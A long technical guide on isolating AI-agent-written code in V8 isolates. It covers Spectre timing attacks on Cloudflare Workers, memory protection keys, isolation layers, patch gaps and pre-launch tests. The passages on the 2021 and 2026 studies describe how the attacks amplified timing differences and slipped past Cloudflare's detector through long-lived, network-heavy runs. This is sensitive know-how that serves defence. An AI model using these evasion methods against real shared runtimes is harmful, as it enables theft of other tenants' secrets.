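Agent code may be able to read another tenant's memory even when V8 has no bugs, because the weakness is in the processor. Spectre, disclosed in 2018, is a family of attacks in which a program times its own operations to infer data it isn't allowed to read. According to Cloudflare's *Security model*, Google's V8 team has stated that V8 itself can't defend against Spectre, so whoever runs the isolates needs another defence.

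### How a wrong guess leaks a bit

Fetching a value from main memory takes a processor as long as running hundreds of instructions. When a program reaches an `if` whose condition depends on such a value, the processor predicts the outcome from past behavior and carries on without waiting. This is called speculative execution. It saves time when the prediction is right, and when it's wrong, the processor discards the results and takes the other path.

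Suppose a program adds up an array of invoice amounts and checks before each read that the index is within the array. After thousands of successful checks, the processor predicts that the next one will succeed too. If the next index is outside the array, the processor may read whatever is in memory there before the check finishes. It then discards the value, and the JavaScript program behaves exactly as the language requires.

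But the processor doesn't undo changes to its cache, the small, fast memory that holds recently used data. If the discarded work loaded different data depending on whether a secret bit was 0 or 1, some reads will be a few nanoseconds faster than others. A program that can measure the difference can determine the bit.

Unlike many attacks on software, this one doesn't require a flaw in the victim's program. The attacker's own program can both make the processor guess wrong and measure the result.

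### Why isolates are more exposed

Isolates in one process share an address space, so a speculative read can reach another isolate's heap. *Dynamic Process Isolation* (Schwarzl, Borrello and colleagues, 2021) explains that updates from processor makers stop one process from influencing the processor's predictions in another, but don't help when attacker and victim share a process. Virtual machines are also vulnerable to Spectre, but operating systems and hypervisors can block many known attacks between processes or between virtual machines.

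Browser makers responded by putting different sites in different processes. Cloudflare found that this took too much memory and processor time. When Schwarzl and colleagues forced typical lightweight Workers into separate processes, each used two to five times as much memory and eight times as much processor time. For one unusually demanding Worker, memory use rose by 20% to 70% and processor time by about 60%. A separate process therefore adds proportionally less overhead to programs that do a lot of computing.

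With agent code, the host is also a likely victim. On a large platform, an attacker normally has to get a program into the same process as the target. But a Dynamic Worker usually shares its host's thread, so the host's access tokens may already be in the same process as the agent's program.

### Taking away the clock

Cloudflare tries to prevent a program from timing itself. In a deployed Worker, both of JavaScript's usual clocks stand still while code runs and advance only after input or output, such as a network request:

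```js
const start = Date.now();
compareAllTickets();
const end = Date.now();   // the same value as start
```

Browser makers instead made their clocks less precise. That only slows an attack, because the attacker can repeat a measurement many times and average out the errors.

Cloudflare adds several other defences:

- Workers have no threads or shared memory. With them, a program could build its own clock by having a second thread count as fast as it can.
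- Customers can't upload native code. Processors have instructions that read a precise timer or remove chosen data from the cache, and JavaScript and WebAssembly give no direct access to them.
- Cloudflare can restart the whole runtime daily, which changes where everything lies in memory, and can move Workers to other machines.
- If a Worker behaves suspiciously, Cloudflare moves it into a process of its own.

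None of this affects a clock on another machine. A program can send a message to an outside server, do some work and send another message, and the server can measure the time between them. Network delay varies by far more than the few nanoseconds the attacker is trying to detect, so the attacker has to enlarge that difference and repeat the measurement.

Cloudflare argues that the defences reinforce one another. A slow attack gives Cloudflare time to detect the program, move it or restart the runtime, and each of these slows the attack further. The argument depends on the attack being slow to begin with.

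### The 2021 study

Schwarzl and colleagues, most of them at Graz University of Technology, tested that assumption in 2019 and early 2020 with access to Cloudflare's source code. On a local copy of the Workers runtime, their attack repeated the speculative read 250,000 times for each bit, so that tiny timing differences added up to one that an outside clock could detect. The attack read one bit about every 30 seconds, or about 120 bits an hour.

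This was an estimate of the best an attacker could do. In *Dynamic Process Isolation* (2021), Cloudflare's post about the research, Varda explains that the "remote" clock was on the same machine, which was otherwise idle. The attack was also given the secret's location, which a real attacker would have to find. To calculate the rate, the researchers assumed that every speculative read worked, although their optimised version succeeded only 54% of the time. At the time, Workers could run for only 50 milliseconds by default, far too short to leak a bit this way.

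The researchers still saw the result as a warning, because similar attacks had been slow at first and become practical with more engineering. They built a detector, Dynamic Process Isolation, that uses the processor's built-in counters to look for the unusual behaviour of a Spectre attack.

An attack repeatedly runs a small piece of code with many branches. The detector divides the number of branches by the number of lookups in the iTLB, a table the processor uses to find instructions in memory. A tight loop needs fewer lookups than code that jumps around a large program, so an attack has a high ratio. In the tests, the attack's ratio was 34 standard deviations above the average for ordinary Workers.

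The researchers then measured how many ordinary Workers each threshold would flag on production machines:

| Branches per lookup | Ordinary Workers flagged |
|---|---|
| 1,024 | 21.41% |
| 4,096 | 0.61% |
| 8,192 | 0.26% |
| 65,536 | None |

The researchers chose a threshold of 4,096. A false alarm does little harm, because the Worker keeps running in its new process, only less efficiently. If an isolated Worker uses eight times the processor time, isolating 0.61% of otherwise similar Workers adds about 4% to total processor time. Reading the counters adds another 2%. The researchers rejected a second detection method, which recorded every wrong guess, because it slowed the production system by 50%.

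The chosen detector caught the researchers' own attack and 13 sample Spectre programs. When they slowed the attack enough to stay below the detection threshold, it leaked only about one bit an hour. They couldn't measure how many real attacks the detector missed, because they assumed nobody was attacking the production system. Cloudflare deployed the detector and reported that it wrongly flagged about 20 of the many thousands of Workers on its platform.

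### Twelve bits a second in production

A much faster attack became public in August 2026. *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service* (Schwarzl, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes work that researchers at Cloudflare and the University of Edinburgh did in 2024 and early 2025. They ran the attack on Cloudflare's production machines, alongside customers' traffic and with the defences switched on.

The researchers controlled both the attacking Worker and the victim. They placed a JSON Web Token, a signed string that a program presents to a service to prove who it is acting for, in the victim's memory. The attacking Worker read the token bit by bit. In a related test on known data, the attack leaked up to 12 bits a second with an average accuracy of 99.16%, and the researchers report similar figures for the token.

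A token of 200 characters contains 1,600 bits. The difference in speed is a factor of 360:

| | 2021 study | 2026 study |
|---|---|---|
| Setting | Local copy with no other load | Production machine |
| Highest rate | 120 bits an hour | 12 bits a second |
| Calculation | 1,600 ÷ 120 | 1,600 ÷ 12 |
| Time for the token | About 13 hours 20 minutes | About 2 minutes 13 seconds |

At 99.16% accuracy, one reading of the token would contain about 13 wrong bits, and even one wrong bit would make the token useless. An attacker could read it three times and use the majority value for each bit. That would take less than seven minutes and, if the errors were independent, leave fewer than one wrong bit on average. The attacker would also need time to prepare the attack and find the token.

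The researchers achieved the highest rate under favourable conditions, working at night on a chosen machine whose processors were 10% to 25% busy, with the clock on the same machine. Their attempts failed more often when the machine was busier. But the timing difference remained measurable throughout a 28-hour test, and in a separate comparison even a clock about 1,200 kilometres away was precise enough to distinguish a 0 bit from a 1. Load and distance therefore slow the attack but don't reliably prevent it.

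### Why the detector missed it

Dynamic Process Isolation moved a suspicious program only after the program had finished. The researchers could make one run last from five to more than 20 hours by keeping a network connection active. At 12 bits a second, an attacker could read 27 kilobytes in five hours.

The connection also kept the counters from revealing the attack. Exchanging messages with the outside clock made the processor run a lot of ordinary networking code, which increased the number of instruction lookups and brought the ratio below the threshold. The attacking Worker then looked like any other Worker with heavy network traffic.

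Schwarzl and colleagues call both problems fundamental limits of this kind of detection. That seems too strong for the first, because a detector can check a program while it is still running. The second is harder to solve because many legitimate programs use the network heavily, and an attacker can choose how much traffic to add.

Schwarzl and Pedersen report in *A revisit of remote Spectre attacks on Cloudflare Workers* that Cloudflare has since changed the detector to handle long-running and network-heavy programs. Cloudflare is also investigating whether the pattern of messages to an outside clock could reveal an attack. It has added the V8 heap sandbox and memory protection keys, which are a processor feature. Corry and Gupta estimate in *Safe in the sandbox* that randomly assigned keys would stop 92% of reads between isolates.

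In a local test, the researchers confirmed that the heap sandbox blocks the speculative read they had used. Schwarzl and Pedersen caution that neither the heap sandbox nor the keys fully defend against Spectre, since other variants may still work.

### Cloudflare's claim and its reply

In its *Security model* documentation, written before the new attack became public, Cloudflare describes its approach as "resistant to the entire range of Spectre-style attacks". It says its own adversarial tests had not produced a remote timing attack that worked in production, and that any such attack would take at least hours and perhaps weeks.

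The 2026 result contradicts this. A daily restart might interrupt an attack that needs 13 hours to read a token, but it does little against one that needs two minutes. The documentation is still right that Spectre has no complete fix and that outside clocks remain a risk.

The documentation and the 2026 paper also differ on which customers share a process. Cloudflare says it runs several copies of the runtime on each machine and keeps free-plan customers apart from Enterprise customers. Schwarzl and colleagues report a single runtime process per machine. A customer who relies on that separation would need to ask Cloudflare which description is current.

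In response to the research, Cloudflare said it had already mitigated the attack and had found no sign that anyone had exploited it in the previous three years. The new barriers support the claim of mitigation, at least for the attack the researchers built. The lack of any sign of exploitation is weaker evidence, because the detector meant to notice such attacks had missed this one, and Cloudflare doesn't explain what other records it checked.

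### Keeping secrets out of the process

A Spectre attack within a process can't read a secret that was never in that process's memory. The 2026 paper discusses LeakLess, a design that keeps secrets in a separate process or on another machine and adds them to requests as they leave. Developers have to mark each secret by hand, and code that needs to compute with a secret can't easily use the design.

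For the support agent, a small service on another machine could hold the mail token. The host function would check the ticket and call this service to send the approved template. Moving the token to a second Worker wouldn't be enough, because both Workers could run in the same process.

The host still needs a credential to contact the mail service, and agent code might steal it, so the credential should expire quickly and allow only the approved kind of email. Customer records also pass through the host's memory, so the host should fetch only the fields it needs and avoid caching them.

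### Removing outside clocks

Schwarzl and colleagues conclude that a platform can't prevent remote timing if a program may connect to outside servers. Setting `globalOutbound` to `null` therefore protects against remote timing as well as stolen data leaving through `fetch()`. If a program needs network access, the host should allow only the destinations it needs and refuse connections that stay open. In the 2026 research, messages over an open connection didn't count towards the subrequest limit, so a low limit alone wouldn't have stopped them.

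Blocking the network doesn't remove every way to measure time. A Worker's clock advances after input or output, which may include some stub calls. Its resolution is only about a millisecond, but the researchers found this was enough once they enlarged the timing difference. A user who submits a program can also measure how long the answer takes to arrive, although the model's response time would make this very imprecise.

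The host can limit how many timing measurements a program makes. The researchers needed 5 to 40 timed samples per bit. If every stub call provided one sample, a cap of 250 calls would let a program read at most 50 bits, before subtracting the calls needed to prepare the attack. Stubs should also leave precise times out of their results unless the task needs them.

### Ending programs quickly

At 12 bits a second, a program with 200 milliseconds of processor time could leak two or three bits. It would probably leak none, because the attack's setup has to be repeated on every run. One setup step tested 100 known values, which would take about eight seconds at the same speed. Cloudflare's example of custom limits is stricter, with 10 milliseconds of processor time and five subrequests.

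The researchers kept resetting their program's processor-time limit by sending it messages, so the host should also enforce a deadline for the whole run that the program can't extend, and refuse incoming connections to agent code. Starting each program in a new isolate forces an attacker to repeat the preparation. A hostile user can still submit many programs, which is another reason to cap the number per task.

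These limits matter more for developers who host isolates themselves. A plain V8 isolate has a working `Date`, and Cloudflare's open-source runtime, workerd, lets its clocks run freely in local development, according to Cloudflare's *Performance and timers*. Developers who run workerd on their own servers would need to test whether the clock stops there.

A running clock can make an attack much faster. In the 2021 comparison, a browser attack from Google leaked about 76 bits a second with a clock accurate to a millisecond, although it read only its own isolate's memory. A developer using isolated-vm would also have to build any detection like Cloudflare's themselves. But with a few dozen tenants, they can often give each one a separate process and keep the host's secrets in another, which is impractical for Cloudflare with thousands.

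## Choosing, patching and testing the layers around the isolate

Several barriers can contain a program that escapes its isolate, including a separate process for each tenant, and their overhead varies widely.

### What each layer contains and costs

The table covers the case where agent code has used a flaw in V8 or in the library around the isolate to take control of its process.

| Arrangement | What it contains | What the attacker can still use | Cost |
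|---|---|---|---|
| All tenants in one process | Nothing | Other tenants' data, and the process's tokens, files and network | A few milliseconds and a few megabytes per isolate |
| One process per tenant | Crashes and corrupted memory; it also hinders timing attacks between tenants | The process's own files and network access | Up to ten times the processor use at Cloudflare's scale |
| A process with no files or network | Theft through files or new connections | Data already in the process; bugs in the kernel | Mostly the work of setting it up |
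| A container | Whatever its settings forbid | Bugs in the kernel, which neighbouring containers share | Typically hundreds of milliseconds and hundreds of megabytes |
| A virtual machine | Bugs in its own kernel as well | Bugs in the hypervisor; shared disks and hardware | The memory of a whole guest system, plus a small overhead |

None of these layers stops a program from misusing its stubs.

A layer also protects only what lies outside it. If the support agent's host shares a virtual machine with agent code, a program that takes over that machine gets the host's access tokens too. A safer layout puts the host elsewhere:

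```
Host                                  Virtual machine for agent code
stub functions, access tokens,  <-->  runner process, no files or network
call counts, logs               JSON    isolate: the model's program
```

The runner is the process that contains the isolate. After an escape, an attacker can send the host any message the runner could have sent, so the host itself has to check arguments and count calls. If several tenants share a runner, the attacker can also impersonate another tenant. Giving each tenant a separate runner and socket lets the host identify the tenant by the connection rather than by the message's contents.

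Heavy layers take much more time and memory than light ones, though the gap varies by product. According to Varda and colleagues, an isolate takes a few milliseconds to start and uses a few megabytes of memory, while a container needs hundreds of each. If a thousand programs were waiting for slow services at once, isolates of 3 megabytes each would need 3 gigabytes of memory, while containers of 300 megabytes each would need 300 gigabytes.

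Start-up times have since fallen. InfoQ (2026) reports that Daytona, which sells sandboxes for agents, claims to create one from a Docker container in under 90 milliseconds. If the hundredfold difference Cloudflare gave in March applied to its own containers, the sixfold improvement in September would have reduced it to about seventeenfold.

Virtual machines have become lighter too. Firecracker, which Amazon's cloud division released as open source in 2018, runs microVMs, virtual machines with only a few simulated devices. Browserbase puts Firecracker's memory overhead at less than 5 mebibytes per machine and says that programs run about 2% to 8% slower than without virtualisation. The memory figure covers only the host's bookkeeping, so the guest's kernel, Node.js and the program need additional memory.

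One server can create 150 of these microVMs a second. A service that runs a million programs a month needs about 0.4 a second on average, and about 39 a second at a peak of a hundred times the average. One server can therefore create microVMs fast enough for an operator of that size, though the delay before each program starts might still be a reason to avoid them. Creating a million sandboxes a second, as in Cloudflare's example, would take about 6,700 such servers.

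Cloudflare's figure of ten times the processor time for separate processes comes from a platform where many requests need less than a millisecond. Separate processes should add proportionally less overhead to an agent's program that computes for 20 milliseconds and then waits for a ticket service.

A heavier layer, such as a container, can still leak data through resources that customers share. In September 2026, researchers at Accomplish showed that a customer of Cloudflare's container service could read up to 60 kilobytes that another customer's container had left on disk. SC Media's *Cloudflare Containers vulnerability allowed data leakage* explains that the disk blocks of deleted containers returned to a shared pool without being wiped. The flaw also affected Cloudflare's Sandboxes, which customers use to run agent code.

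Cloudflare (2026) reports that it turned wiping back on, cleared the affected disks and found no sign that anyone else had used the flaw. Antipov (2026), in *Cloudflare отдавала контейнерам чужие данные с диска. Причиной стала одна настройка*, blames a single setting and lists Firecracker among the article's topics. If the affected containers ran in Firecracker, the data passed between customers without a breach of the virtual machine boundary.

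### How Cloudflare closes off the process

The outer sandbox around Cloudflare's shared process uses namespaces and seccomp, two Linux features that containers also rely on. Namespaces give a process a private view of resources such as files and network connections. Seccomp blocks chosen system calls, which are the requests a program makes to the kernel.

Cloudflare's sandbox is stricter than a container's because its restrictions take effect later. A container engine applies its restrictions before it starts the guest program from disk, so it can't forbid all access to files. Cloudflare starts its runtime first, lets it load everything it needs, and then applies the restrictions before loading any customer's isolate. Since the runtime no longer needs the disk, Cloudflare can give it an empty file system and block every system call that deals with files.

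The process can't open network connections either. It can only exchange messages with other local processes, through what Linux calls UNIX domain sockets:

- The supervisor fetches Workers' code and settings.
- The outbound proxy sends requests to the internet. It refuses any that are addressed to Cloudflare's internal services, and adds a header that identifies the Worker, so that Cloudflare can trace abuse.
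- The inbound proxy receives visitors' requests and holds the keys that encrypt web traffic, which the runtime never gets.

A request for a Worker that isn't loaded carries an encryption key for that Worker's code and secrets, and the process must present this key to the supervisor to get the code. An attacker who controlled the process couldn't list the Workers on the machine or load one whose key had never arrived. But the attacker could get the secrets of every Worker already in the process, and of any Worker that received a request there while the attacker remained.

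Cloudflare limits who is in that position by dividing its runtime processes into groups called cordons and assigning Workers to them by how much it trusts each customer. This separates free customers from Enterprise customers, which conflicts with the 2026 timing paper's description.

Some Workers get a private process. For example, a Worker gets one while its developer is debugging it, because V8's debugging interface has had less security testing than the rest of the engine. Varda and colleagues add that Cloudflare scans code for malicious patterns and blocks suspicious programs or puts more layers around them.

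Deno describes a similar design for its hosting service. Each process gets its own namespace, seccomp detects system calls that the process shouldn't make, and the kernel caps its resources. A watchdog stops isolates that stay over their memory limit or block their thread for too long.

### Twelve keys and 16,384 regions

An attacker who takes over the JavaScript heap in a shared process can read another isolate's data without file or network access. Cloudflare guards against this with memory protection keys, a feature of recent processors that labels each area of memory with a small number and lets a thread access only the areas whose labels it currently holds.

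A modern x64 processor has 15 usable keys, and V8 needs a few of them for other purposes, which leaves about 12. Corry and Gupta describe how Cloudflare gave each isolate one of these at random. When a bug lets a program read from another isolate's heap, the read succeeds only if both isolates have the same key:

```
chance that the keys match      1/12   = about 8%
chance that the read is caught  11/12  = about 92%
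```

If the keys don't match, the processor stops the read, and Cloudflare kills the program and investigates. With 1,200 isolates in a process, about 100 would share the attacker's key, but the attacker wouldn't know which. The chance of reading from two randomly chosen neighbours without being caught is 1 in 144.

The V8 heap sandbox allowed Cloudflare to do better, but V8 originally required every isolate in a process to share one sandbox, which limited their JavaScript objects to a combined 4 GiB. That was far too little for thousands of Workers. Cloudflare paid Igalia, a software consultancy, to add support for several heap sandboxes in one process, and now gives each isolate its own.

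Each of Cloudflare's heap sandboxes reserves 8 GiB of addresses, half for objects and half for buffers and other data. A Linux process on most current hardware has 128 TiB of addresses available:

```
128 TiB = 131,072 GiB
131,072 ÷ 8 = 16,384 heap sandboxes
```

This is an upper limit, because the runtime and its libraries need addresses too. Each region must also start at a multiple of 4 GiB, and a program can't make Linux choose such an address. The usual workaround is to request 12 GiB and return what isn't needed, but this leaves gaps that are too small for the next request. If every region had 4 GiB of unusable space beside it, only 10,922 regions would fit.

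The guard regions, which are unusable addresses around a heap sandbox, take up far more address space than the sandbox itself. An attacker who corrupts an array's length and index can reach up to 32 GiB away, using the largest 32-bit index and 8-byte items, so V8 normally leaves a gap of that size. With one 32 GiB gap for each 8 GiB region, a process could have only 3,276 heap sandboxes.

Cloudflare therefore packs the regions tightly and assigns the keys in a fixed rotation. With 12 keys, the beginning of the sequence looks like this:

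| Position in memory | Key |
|---|---|
| 0 to 8 GiB | 1 |
| 8 to 16 GiB | 2 |
| 16 to 24 GiB | 3 |
| … | … |
| 88 to 96 GiB | 12 |
| 96 to 104 GiB | 1 |

The first region ends at 8 GiB, and the next one with the same key starts at 96 GiB. A stray array access can't cross the 88 GiB between them, so it always lands in a region with a different key, and the processor stops it. The neighbouring heap sandboxes act as guard regions without wasting any addresses. Five keys would be just enough, since four 8 GiB regions, or 32 GiB, would separate any two with the same key.

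Rotation raises the protection against this kind of access from 92% to 100%, but not against an attacker who can read any address in the process. Such an attacker might find a fixed rotation easier to work around than random keys, because every twelfth region has the same key. Corry and Gupta also exclude attackers who can run their own machine code, since those attackers could turn the keys off.

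### The case for isolates and the case for virtual machines

Cloudflare argues that an isolate hardened in these ways is safe enough for agent code, and that isolates are the only sandboxes lightweight enough to discard after one use. Discarding the sandbox keeps traces of one task from carrying over to the next, as they can in a reused container.

An isolate also exposes less of the operating system. Agent code in a virtual machine usually gets a complete Linux system, while code in an isolate can't make a system call unless it breaks V8 or the host's bindings. Because Cloudflare runs the whole platform, it can add defences and install V8's fixes without waiting for its customers.

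Malte Ubl of Vercel, a hosting company that competes with Cloudflare and once ran its own functions there, replies that even Chrome doesn't rely on isolates alone. In his view, any V8 flaw that lets code out of an isolate compromises Cloudflare's platform. He accepts that Cloudflare may be able to take this risk because it can update its servers much faster than Chrome's users update their browsers, but he prefers isolation enforced by the operating system and the processor.

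Cloudflare has some defence in depth, although Ubl suggests otherwise. An attacker who exploits a V8 bug must still get past the confined process, the heap sandboxes and the keys to reach the rest of the platform. But tenants in the same process depend mainly on V8 and its additions to isolate them from each other, and the 2026 timing attack succeeded there.

Companies that sell microVMs make the argument more broadly. Unikraft's *The Mighty (micro)Virtual Machine* says that only the runtime's own logic separates isolates, and that containers share a kernel whose exposed surface is "enormous". A program in a microVM has to get past a boundary that the processor enforces, and the software behind that boundary is deliberately small. Scholz's *Firecracker vs QEMU*, written for the sandbox company E2B, likewise says that people generally don't consider containers secure enough for LLM-written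 code.

Dedalus Labs, which sells virtual machines, concedes that isolates can give "strong practical isolation" on a hardened platform. Its main objection is that much of what agents do isn't JavaScript. An agent that has to compile a program or run a Linux tool needs an operating system, which even a hardened isolate can't provide.

These companies all have something to sell, as does Cloudflare, although it also sells containers. *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* (2026), an independent engineer's post on shayon.dev, makes the more careful point that people call containers, microVMs and WebAssembly modules "isolated" even though each has a different boundary and fails differently.

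Cloudflare publishes workerd, an open-source runtime from the same code base as Workers. In the README, Cloudflare warns that workerd "is not a hardened sandbox" and does not protect well enough against bugs in its own implementation. It says anyone who uses workerd to run possibly malicious code must run it inside a secure sandbox, such as a virtual machine.

So Cloudflare's argument applies to its whole platform, including the people who maintain it. A company that installs workerd gets the isolates without the supervisor, the cordons or the staff who watch for alarms. For that company, a virtual machine is the easier outer layer to get right, because its boundary doesn't depend on a custom build of V8. On Cloudflare itself, a virtual machine has less of an advantage. Hardened isolates are reasonable there for short programs with narrow stubs, but a tenant whose secrets would be worth an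 expensive attack should keep them out of the shared process.

### The patch gap

Once V8's developers publish a fix, attackers can compare the old and new code, find the flaw and attack systems that haven't installed the fix. The patch gap is the time between the fix's publication and its deployment in production. Chromium's *Chrome Security Update FAQ* says that attacking a known flaw during this gap is easier and cheaper than attacking an undiscovered one. It recommends installing all updates promptly rather than prioritizing fixes for flaws that attackers are known to use, since nobody sees every attack.

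| System | Time from public fix to use |
|---|---|
| Cloudflare Workers | Under 24 hours |
| Chrome, by an earlier Google announcement | 15 days, down from 33 |
| Chrome in July 2026 | Typically weeks by the ordinary route, with a faster one for serious flaws |

Cloudflare's systems build a new runtime as soon as V8's developers publish a patch. After human reviewers approve it with one click, the release goes out automatically. Cloudflare says in SecurityBrief UK that some security teams now aim to install fixes within two hours, but it doesn't think speed alone will solve the problem.

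Google has also sped up its Chrome releases. It copies serious fixes straight into the version that most people use, releases security updates weekly and is trying twice-weekly ones. With Chrome 153, on 8 September 2026, it moved from a new version every four weeks to one every two. *Fresher features, faster fixes* (Mason and Ravichandran, 2026) describes this change as a way to shrink the patch gap. A fix still has no effect until the user restarts the browser.

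The fix for CVE-2026-87491, one of the V8 flaws that attackers were already using, came out the same day. Google had received the report 33 days earlier, according to Help Net Security, so even a fully updated system can be vulnerable for weeks before a fix is available. The patch gap began after Google received the report, when the corrected code became public.

Anyone embedding V8 also has to stay on a version that still receives fixes. Varda explained in a Hacker News discussion that a security patch generally reaches all of V8's active branches at about the same time, but the old stable branch becomes obsolete when Chrome moves on. Workers has to change branches before then to keep receiving fixes. In the same discussion, oldmanhorton pointed out that running ahead of Chrome means using V8 versions that have had less testing. With Chrome's shorter cycle, anyone who follows its stable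 branch will probably have to upgrade more often.

Few self-hosters can keep up with this. A developer who uses isolated-vm gets V8 from Node.js, whose long-term releases stay on one version of V8 well after Google has abandoned it. The Node.js maintainers have to copy fixes back into the old version. Suppose they take eight days over one fix, the company's supplier takes three more to put the new Node.js into its server image, and the company deploys once a week:

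```
day 0    V8's developers publish the fix
day 8    a Node.js release includes it
day 11   the supplier's server image includes that release
day 18   the company's next weekly deployment, at the latest
```

The attacker in this example has up to 18 days, compared with less than one at Cloudflare, even though nobody is careless. The company controls only the last seven days, which it could shorten by deploying as soon as an image appears. Building the image itself would save another three days.

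Warm processes and virtual machines can prolong the gap. A runner that started on day 17 still has the old V8 in memory on day 19 unless the deployment replaces it. Every runner therefore needs a maximum age, just as a browser needs a restart to apply an update.

The library and the runtime need their own updates. Aikido lists a use-after-free flaw in workerd versions released between 26 February and 7 March 2026 that could let crafted requests crash the runtime. An operator who followed only V8's announcements would have missed it.

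OpenWorkers is an open-source system modelled on Cloudflare Workers. In a thread with posts by max_lt and AgentME, its developer admits that the project can't compete with Cloudflare's 24-hour patches and years of hardening. The developer now recommends it for running a company's own code on its own servers. The same limit is sensible for any self-hosted isolate without another layer around it.

If a serious V8 flaw becomes public before a fixed runtime is available, a self-hoster can stop running agent code and fall back on ordinary tool calls. If the bug is in one of V8's optimising compilers, they can switch off those compilers instead. Both are much easier with a setting prepared in advance.

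### Matching the layers to the risk

The choice of layers depends mostly on who can influence the program and whose data is in the same process. The table gives a minimum for each combination on an operator's own servers.

| Who can influence the code | One tenant's data in the process | Several tenants' data in the process |
|---|---|---|
| Only the company's developers, who review it before it runs | An isolate in the application's process | The same, with separate processes if a crash would affect too many people |
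| A model that reads only the company's own trusted data | An isolate in a separate process with no files or network | One such process per tenant |
| A model that reads text from outsiders | The same process, inside a container or virtual machine that contains no secrets | One virtual machine per tenant |
| Anyone who can submit a program or tell the model what to write | A virtual machine used for one task or conversation | Avoid this; give each tenant a virtual machine |

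An operator on a managed platform such as Cloudflare's can accept the last column for short programs if the provider maintains the outer layers and the operator keeps valuable secrets elsewhere. In every row but the first, code that needs Linux programs should run in a virtual machine.

The employee's support agent falls in the third row because strangers write the tickets. One company owns all the data, so a single virtual machine can run the programs, each in a new isolate. If the company opens the agent to customers such as Ana, the agent moves to the fourth row. The company then needs to either give each conversation its own virtual machine or use a managed platform and pass in only the logged-in customer's record.

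The README for workerd includes a sample configuration for systemd, the program that starts services on most Linux systems. The sample runs workerd as a user with few privileges and stops it from gaining more. That doesn't meet the README's own warning, because an attacker who took over the process could still read many files and open connections. Four more lines would close off much of this:

```ini
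[Service]
User=nobody
NoNewPrivileges=true
PrivateNetwork=true
ProtectSystem=strict
ProtectHome=true
MemoryMax=1G
```

`PrivateNetwork` cuts the process off from the network, but the process keeps any sockets that systemd opened for it beforehand and can still reach the host through a UNIX domain socket. The next two lines make the file system read-only and hide users' home directories. `MemoryMax` makes the kernel stop the service if it uses more than a gigabyte of memory. The process can still read system files, so this setup is weaker than Cloudflare's empty file system and belongs inside the virtual machine as an additional barrier.

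### Tests to run before launch

A test written as agent code checks only the isolate. Even if `fetch()` fails inside the isolate, the process around it may still have full network access, and nobody will notice until an escape. Each outer layer needs a test that assumes the inner ones have failed. The simplest method is to run a small native program under exactly the same restrictions as the runner. The program stands in for an attacker who already controls the process.

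| What to test | How | Passes if |
|---|---|---|
| Files | Try to read a file and write one, first from the isolate and then from the native program | Both attempts fail in both places, apart from reads the operator has deliberately allowed |
| Network | Try an outside address, the company's internal services and the cloud provider's address for machine credentials | No connection opens, and the outside server's log is empty |
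| Secrets | Put recognisable fake tokens wherever the host keeps real ones, then search the runner's memory and environment | The search finds none |
| Other tenants | Give tenant B a marked record, then request it as tenant A through every stub | The host refuses each request and logs it |
| Leftovers | Save a marker in a global variable, a file and the virtual disk, then run another tenant's program | The second program finds no trace of it |
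| Processor limit | Run an endless loop | The loop stops at about the limit, and a second program keeps running |
| Deadline | Wait for a promise that never settles, and have a stub call ready for afterwards | The run ends at 30 seconds, and the host refuses the late call |
| Memory | Fill the heap, then fill large buffers | The program or its runner stops, and the host survives |
| Call limit | Make one call more than the limit, both in sequence and in parallel | The host refuses exactly one call each time |
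| Logging | Run a program that makes 201 calls | The log has 201 entries with the right user and program |
| Versions | Compare V8, the runtime and the wrapper library with their newest security releases | All are current, and no runner is older than its maximum age |

In Node.js, `process.versions.v8` gives the version of V8. An old version may still contain a newer fix, because the Node.js maintainers may have backported it. The operator should therefore check that Node.js itself is the latest release in a line that still gets updates.

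The tests belong in the deployment process, where a failure can block a release. Several faults described earlier, such as a misspelt `globalOutbound` or a changed import line, break a protection without producing an error. A new version of Node.js or a later compatibility date can do the same. It is also worth breaking each protection once, for instance by removing the network restriction, to confirm that its test fails.

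### Testing V8 and workerd themselves

Teams that compile V8 or write C++ bindings for it can test the V8 heap sandbox. Chromium documents a build setting, `v8_enable_memory_corruption_api = true`, that lets a test program change any memory inside that sandbox, as an attacker with a V8 bug could.

With `--sandbox-testing`, V8 exits normally after a harmless crash, such as one that stays within the heap sandbox, so an automated test passes. With `--sandbox-fuzzing`, V8 reports an error instead, so a fuzzer can detect that its program ended early. Both modes use a Linux-only filter to separate harmless crashes from damage outside the heap sandbox.

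Both modes also report reads outside the heap sandbox as violations, although the sandbox's guarantee doesn't cover reads. An operator whose tenants share a process shouldn't dismiss those reports. The special build must never reach production, because it lets any program it runs corrupt memory. Most operators don't compile V8 and need only confirm that their copy has the heap sandbox turned on.

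V8's tests don't cover the functions that a runtime adds, such as workerd's `fetch()`. In August 2025, mschwarzl (2025) proposed a change that lets Google's fuzzer Fuzzilli test workerd. Fuzzilli normally keeps an engine running and feeds it one program after another, which is much faster than restarting it for each program. The change adds the shared memory and pipes that workerd needs for this, and a command to start it in that mode.

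Before a fuzzing run, Fuzzilli deliberately crashes the target in several ways to check that it will detect a real crash. A team that adds its own C++ functions to workerd can use the same interface, but it has to describe those functions to the fuzzer, or the generated programs will rarely call them with useful arguments. This kind of fuzzing finds crashes and memory errors, but it won't detect a stub that returns the wrong customer's record, so the tests with marked records are still needed.
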